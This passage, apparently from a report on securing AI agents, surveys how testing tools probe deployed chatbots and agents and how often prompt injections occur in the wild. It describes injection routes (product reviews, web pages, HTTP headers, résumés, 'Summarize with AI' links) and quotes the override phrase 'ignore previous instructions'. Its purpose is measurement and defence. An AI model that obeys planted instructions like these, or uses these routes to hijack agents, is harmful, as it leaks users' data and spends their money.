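To find such faults, a tester has to attack the running product through the same connection its users have. For a chat widget, this means sending messages to the HTTP or WebSocket address that the chat window uses. If the browser sends the conversation history with each HTTP request, the tester also has to try altering old messages, or they will miss a flaw like Eurostar's. If a WebSocket connection holds the conversation, the tester should open a new connection for each independent test, because earlier attacks would otherwise remain in the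 context and might influence later results.

Conversation alone won't reveal everything. Yang, Zheng and colleagues (2026), in *Securing the AI Agent*, describe AI-Infra-Guard, a free testing tool from the Chinese company Tencent, which uses a different method for each of four layers:

- **Infrastructure:** fixed rules compare the software on a server with more than 1,400 known vulnerabilities.
- **Tools:** a language model examines an MCP server's code and tool descriptions for flaws that no simple rule could express.
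- **Agent behaviour:** a language model holds conversations of several turns with the deployed agent, without access to its code.
- **Model:** the software sends many reworded harmful requests, and another model judges the replies.

When AI-Infra-Guard converses with a deployed agent, it escalates its attacks in stages and follows rules about when to stop, because every message costs money and the service may limit how many it can send. It confirms leaks with *canary tokens*, unique strings that no legitimate reply would contain. A hostile MCP server could include instructions for the auditing model to report that the code is safe, so Yang and colleagues treat everything the tool examines as untrusted.

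In *Black-Box Red Teaming of Agentic AI*, Kumar, Birur and colleagues (2026) tested a restaurant receptionist and a stock adviser only through their public interfaces, trying four models in each. They conclude that a system's architecture matters more than the choice of model. That may be true, but the two systems differed in task, framework and number of agents, so the experiment can't show which difference mattered. The researchers also discarded scenarios that drew no worrying response from a baseline agent, which probably raised some of their published risk scores. Those scores run as high as 85 per cent. The researchers work for Enkrypt AI, a security vendor.

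A test that finds nothing is even harder to interpret, because the agent may have resisted the attack or the attack may never have reached it. *GreyZone* (Zhou, Jiang and colleagues, 2026) addresses this with a benchmark for the testing tools themselves. It contains 46 attack scenarios in ten open-source applications, including a shop, a banking assistant and an email agent. Each scenario specifies a starting state, a security policy, the violation the attacker wants to cause and what they are allowed to do. A separate program called an *oracle* checks whether the violation took place.

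In one scenario, the attacker is a seller on the shopping platform Shopware who can write a product review. He wants the buyer's agent to email him the customer's account and order details. The oracle checks the outgoing email for real customer data. It ignores the testing tool's verdict and the agent's own account of what it did, because an agent can claim to have sent an email when it didn't, or send one without mentioning it. Afterwards, the software restores the shop from a saved copy so one attack can't affect the next.

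Zhou and colleagues also treat a timeout or a failed delivery as missing evidence, not as a successful defence. They have connected four testing tools to the benchmark but so far report only two preliminary case studies, both with one of them, Promptfoo, so GreyZone doesn't yet show which tool finds the most flaws. GreyZone replaces some outside services with imitations, such as an emulator in place of Gmail. This makes the tests repeatable and harmless, but they might miss a flaw in how an agent connects to the real Gmail.

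## How common are these attacks outside tests?

Planted instructions are rare on the public web, and most of those that researchers have found are pranks or attempts to keep AI systems away. It is much harder to establish how often they hijack real agents, because published figures may count planted instructions, agents that read them, agents that obey them or people harmed. A count of planted instructions doesn't measure the other three, because agents may never read the instructions, may ignore them, or may obey them without causing harm, for example by writing a silly summary.

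### Instructions planted on web pages

In *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, Khodayari, Acharya and colleagues (2026) searched about half of the October 2025 edition of Common Crawl, the public web archive. They looked for 3,963 phrases such as "ignore previous instructions" at 1.2 billion web addresses, then checked the matches, partly by hand, to remove tutorials and news articles about prompt injection. They confirmed 12,075 planted instructions on 9,676 pages, or about eight pages per million. Only 285 of the 24.8 million hosts in the sample had any.

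Site operators had planted 81 per cent of these instructions on their own pages. Only 220 instructions, on 127 pages, were in comments and other posts by visitors, the route an attacker would use to reach Ana's agent through a review.

Khodayari and colleagues found another 3,312 instructions through Censys and Shodan, two services that scan the internet for servers, and sorted the whole collection by purpose. Some instructions had more than one:

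| Purpose | Planted instructions | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Disrupt the AI's work | 8,894 | Return random numbers |
| Protect personal data or copyrighted text | 4,093 | Do not train on this content |
| Detect bots | 3,096 | Include a certain word in the reply |
| Unclear | 2,632 | Drop the current task and do another |
| Promote a business, source or person | 1,521 | Give only a positive review |
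| Steal data | 13 | Reveal the system prompt |

Google also searched Common Crawl, where each monthly edition contains 2 to 3 billion pages. It looked for known phrases, used its Gemini model to classify the intent of each match, and had people review the results. According to Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild* (2026), Google published its findings in April. It found pranks, guidance for AI summaries, self-promotion and attempts to deter agents, including one that lured them to a page that never finished loading. A smaller group of instructions was malicious, intended to steal data or delete files.

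The number of malicious instructions Google found grew by 32 per cent between November 2025 and February 2026. Google gives no absolute numbers, so the rise could be from 25 cases to 33 or from 2,500 to 3,300. If the numbers were small, a few website owners could account for the whole increase. Google found that most of the malicious instructions were simple and seemed to be experiments or pranks by individual site owners.

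Unit 42 used its own internet monitoring data instead of a public archive. It describes twelve cases, including a page that told agents to send $5,000 through PayPal. The most elaborate was a scam ad for "military glasses" that contained 24 attempts to get an automated ad checker to approve it. Unit 42 knows of no confirmed case in which this kind of attack fooled an ad checker in real use.

In Unit 42's data, 14.2 per cent of injections were meant to destroy data, while destructive commands make up about 1 per cent of Khodayari and colleagues' collection. Unit 42 doesn't say how many pages it examined, and its text and chart give different figures (9.5 and 5.5 per cent) for the share meant to get past content moderation. It rates severity by what the injection was meant to do, so a comment that tells an AI to delete its database counts as critical even if no agent that reads it has a database.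 Unit 42's parent company, Palo Alto Networks, sells protection against these attacks.

Adding up the vendors' reports would count some websites more than once. Infosecurity Magazine's *Researchers Uncover 10 In-the-Wild Prompt Injection Payloads Targeting AI Agents* covers ten injections found by the security company Forcepoint. OffSeq's *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* (2026) also lists Forcepoint's findings, and at least one of the sites in it is on Unit 42's list too.

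The newest figures concern HTTP headers, the technical information that a server sends with a page but a browser doesn't display. Andrews (2026), in *Prompt injection in HTTP headers*, examined 217 million responses from Common Crawl's September 2026 edition and found injection attempts on 30 sites, 22 of which were pranks. Her employer, Signals Corps, sells security for agents, so it has little reason to understate the problem.

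### What the crawls miss

These searches are best at finding crude injections. Khodayari and colleagues report that 99 per cent of the instructions directly told the model to abandon its task, but many of the phrases they searched for were instructions of that kind. An injection that resembles a step in the user's task, like those in researchers' demonstrations against browser agents, may contain no suspicious phrase. The attacks found therefore seem unsophisticated partly because of how they were searched for.

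Khodayari and colleagues also acknowledge that they could miss instructions in images or in languages other than English. A site could also show its instructions only to AI agents and send the archive's crawler a harmless page. Andrews found 139 sites with headers that recorded whether the server had classified the visitor as an AI bot. Classifying visitors is the first step in serving AI bots different content, but the headers don't show that these sites did so.

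The largest gap in this evidence is content behind logins. Common Crawl contains little social media and no private email, so it would have missed the invitations and messages that researchers used to hijack Comet and the Claude extension.

### Instructions that reached an agent

If an agent read 100 randomly chosen pages a day, it would come across one of the pages Khodayari and colleagues found about once every three and a half years. A million such agents would together come across about 800 a day. Real agents don't choose pages at random, and the rate was lower on the most popular sites and relatively high on some job and shopping sites.

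People seem to plant instructions much more often where they expect an AI to read them. Search Engine Journal cites a May 2026 study that found hidden injections in about 1 per cent of 196,682 résumés. That is more than a thousand times the rate for web pages. An applicant can reasonably expect screening software to read the résumé, and may get an interview if the injection works.

In February 2026, Microsoft reported a similar practice among companies that want AI assistants to recommend them. Over 60 days, it found 50 different prompts from 31 companies, all of them real businesses, in links sent by email. The links were often behind buttons labelled "Summarize with AI". Clicking one opened the user's assistant with a prompt that asked for a summary and told the assistant to remember the company as a trusted source.

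These prompts were closer to reaching an assistant than text on an unread web page, but someone still had to click the link. Microsoft did not count the clicks or the assistants that stored the instruction. It noted that the effect varied between assistants and changed as their makers added protections.

### Agents that obeyed

Khodayari and colleagues tested 100 of the planted instructions on 13 models. They had each model summarise the page in four formats, which made 5,200 runs. The models followed the planted instruction in 81 runs, or 1.6 per cent. The two commercial models followed it in five of their 800 runs.

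Models obeyed the injected instructions in 3.9 per cent of runs when they received the page as plain text, but in 1.1 per cent when they received its HTML, which can reveal that a passage is hidden from people. A developer who strips the HTML before calling an API may therefore remove a useful warning. But the difference is partly misleading because 20 per cent of the HTML runs ended in errors, mostly when the page was too long for the model. The researchers only asked the models to summarise pages, so the results may not apply to an agent that can send money.

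Some attackers are after money. Infosecurity Magazine's *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents* describes two campaigns that the security vendor Zscaler found. The attackers hid instructions in their sites' pages and raised the sites' search rankings so that agents were more likely to find them. One site posed as software documentation to run a payment scam, and the other impersonated a cryptocurrency service.

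Some website owners may already have evidence of how real agents respond to planted instructions. In Khodayari and colleagues' collection, 598 instructions were *honeypots*, traps meant to make an AI reveal itself, for example by contacting an outside address. The server at that address could record each visit, which would help the owner count the agents that obeyed. These counts would show how often agents follow a harmless order, but not how often they would give away a password.

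### Stolen conversations without an injection

In December 2025, researchers found two Chrome extensions that copied people's conversations with chatbots. OX Security's *900K Users Compromised* reports that one had over 600,000 users and the other over 300,000. The larger one carried Google's "Featured" badge.

The extensions imitated a legitimate AI sidebar from a company called AITOPIA. They had permission to read every website, and they asked the user for consent to collect "anonymous" data. When she opened ChatGPT or DeepSeek, the extension read her messages and the chatbot's replies from the page's DOM. Every 30 minutes it sent this text and the addresses of her open tabs to the attackers' server. If she uninstalled one extension, it opened the other's page to persuade her to install that instead.

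OX Security reported two malicious Chrome extensions that collected users' AI conversations to Google on 29 December. Both were gone from the store by late January 2026, according to Mishcon de Reya's *Malicious Chrome extensions harvest AI conversations from 900K users* (2026). Microsoft confirmed the extensions' activity in the systems of more than 20,000 organisations and found that updates turned data collection back on for users who had refused it.

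The number of victims may be lower than the 900,000 installations, because some people may have installed both extensions and others may never have used ChatGPT or DeepSeek in that browser. OX Security and Microsoft both sell security products, but they described the same behaviour and identified the same servers.

Stealing these conversations didn't require tricking a model, and the Meta account takeovers didn't require an injection. However, Microsoft also saw browser agents download the extensions without the user's explicit approval, apparently because the names and descriptions were convincing. A misleading description can therefore lead a real agent to make a harmful choice, even without a hidden command. Microsoft doesn't say how often this happened.

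### Rare, or rarely recorded?

Confirmed hijackings may be few because the attacks are still rare. Google saw little use of the advanced methods that researchers had published, which supports this explanation. Attackers also have easier options, such as a malicious extension. A security company that found a real victim would have good reason to publicise it, yet Unit 42 didn't name an agent that obeyed the attacker's instructions in any of its twelve cases.

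But hijackings could also go unrecorded. *Hidden prompts in HTML*, from the company Dataprovider, argues that conventional security tools miss injections because there is no malware to detect. A shop's server receives an ordinary request with Ana's cookie and has no record of the review that caused it. The thieves' extensions were easier to investigate than an injection in a single email, because anyone could download the extensions and look for connections to the same few servers.

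This explanation is more convincing for silent data theft than for purchases or messages. Ana might never learn that her agent had leaked an email, but she would probably notice a tablet on her bill, and her friends would notice spam from her account. Even then, she might blame a stolen password rather than the agent.

The logs that could settle the question differ by transport:

| Transport | Who can keep the most useful record | What it can contain | What can be missing |
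|---|---|---|---|
| Direct API | The developer | The full context and every tool call | Requests made later by software that displays the reply |
| Chat widget | The website or plugin vendor | Visitors' messages, replies and tool calls | Forged messages and the passages retrieved from the site |
| Browser agent | The agent's maker | The pages the model read and the actions it chose | Actions by other programs, such as a malicious extension |

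A developer with direct API access is in the best position to test both explanations. The shop could search its returns program's stored emails and tool results for planted instructions, then check whether the next tool call departed from the customer's request. That would show how many instructions reached the agent and how many it obeyed. Finding almost no hijackings in many such logs would be good evidence that they are rare. The logs would contain customers' private data, so the shop would have to protect them and delete them once it no longer needed them.

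The operator of a chat widget could run the same check only if the server stored everything it sent to the model. Many of the plugins Kaya and colleagues studied do not store all of this.

An employer can see only part of the evidence of attacks on browser agents. It can search its computers for known malicious extensions and its network logs for connections to the attackers' servers, as Microsoft recommends. It can also search email and click logs for links to AI assistants with words such as "remember" in the prompt. These searches can show that someone was exposed to an attack, but not whether the assistant followed the attacker's instructions. If the agent runs in a remote browser, its requests to websites don't pass through the employer's network.

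An agent's maker could link the text on a page to the action the agent took next, if it keeps records of both. Google and Anthropic already scan pages while their agents work. Counts of pages scanned, warnings raised and agents that acted on an injection anyway would give a much better estimate of how common these attacks are than another crawl of the public web.
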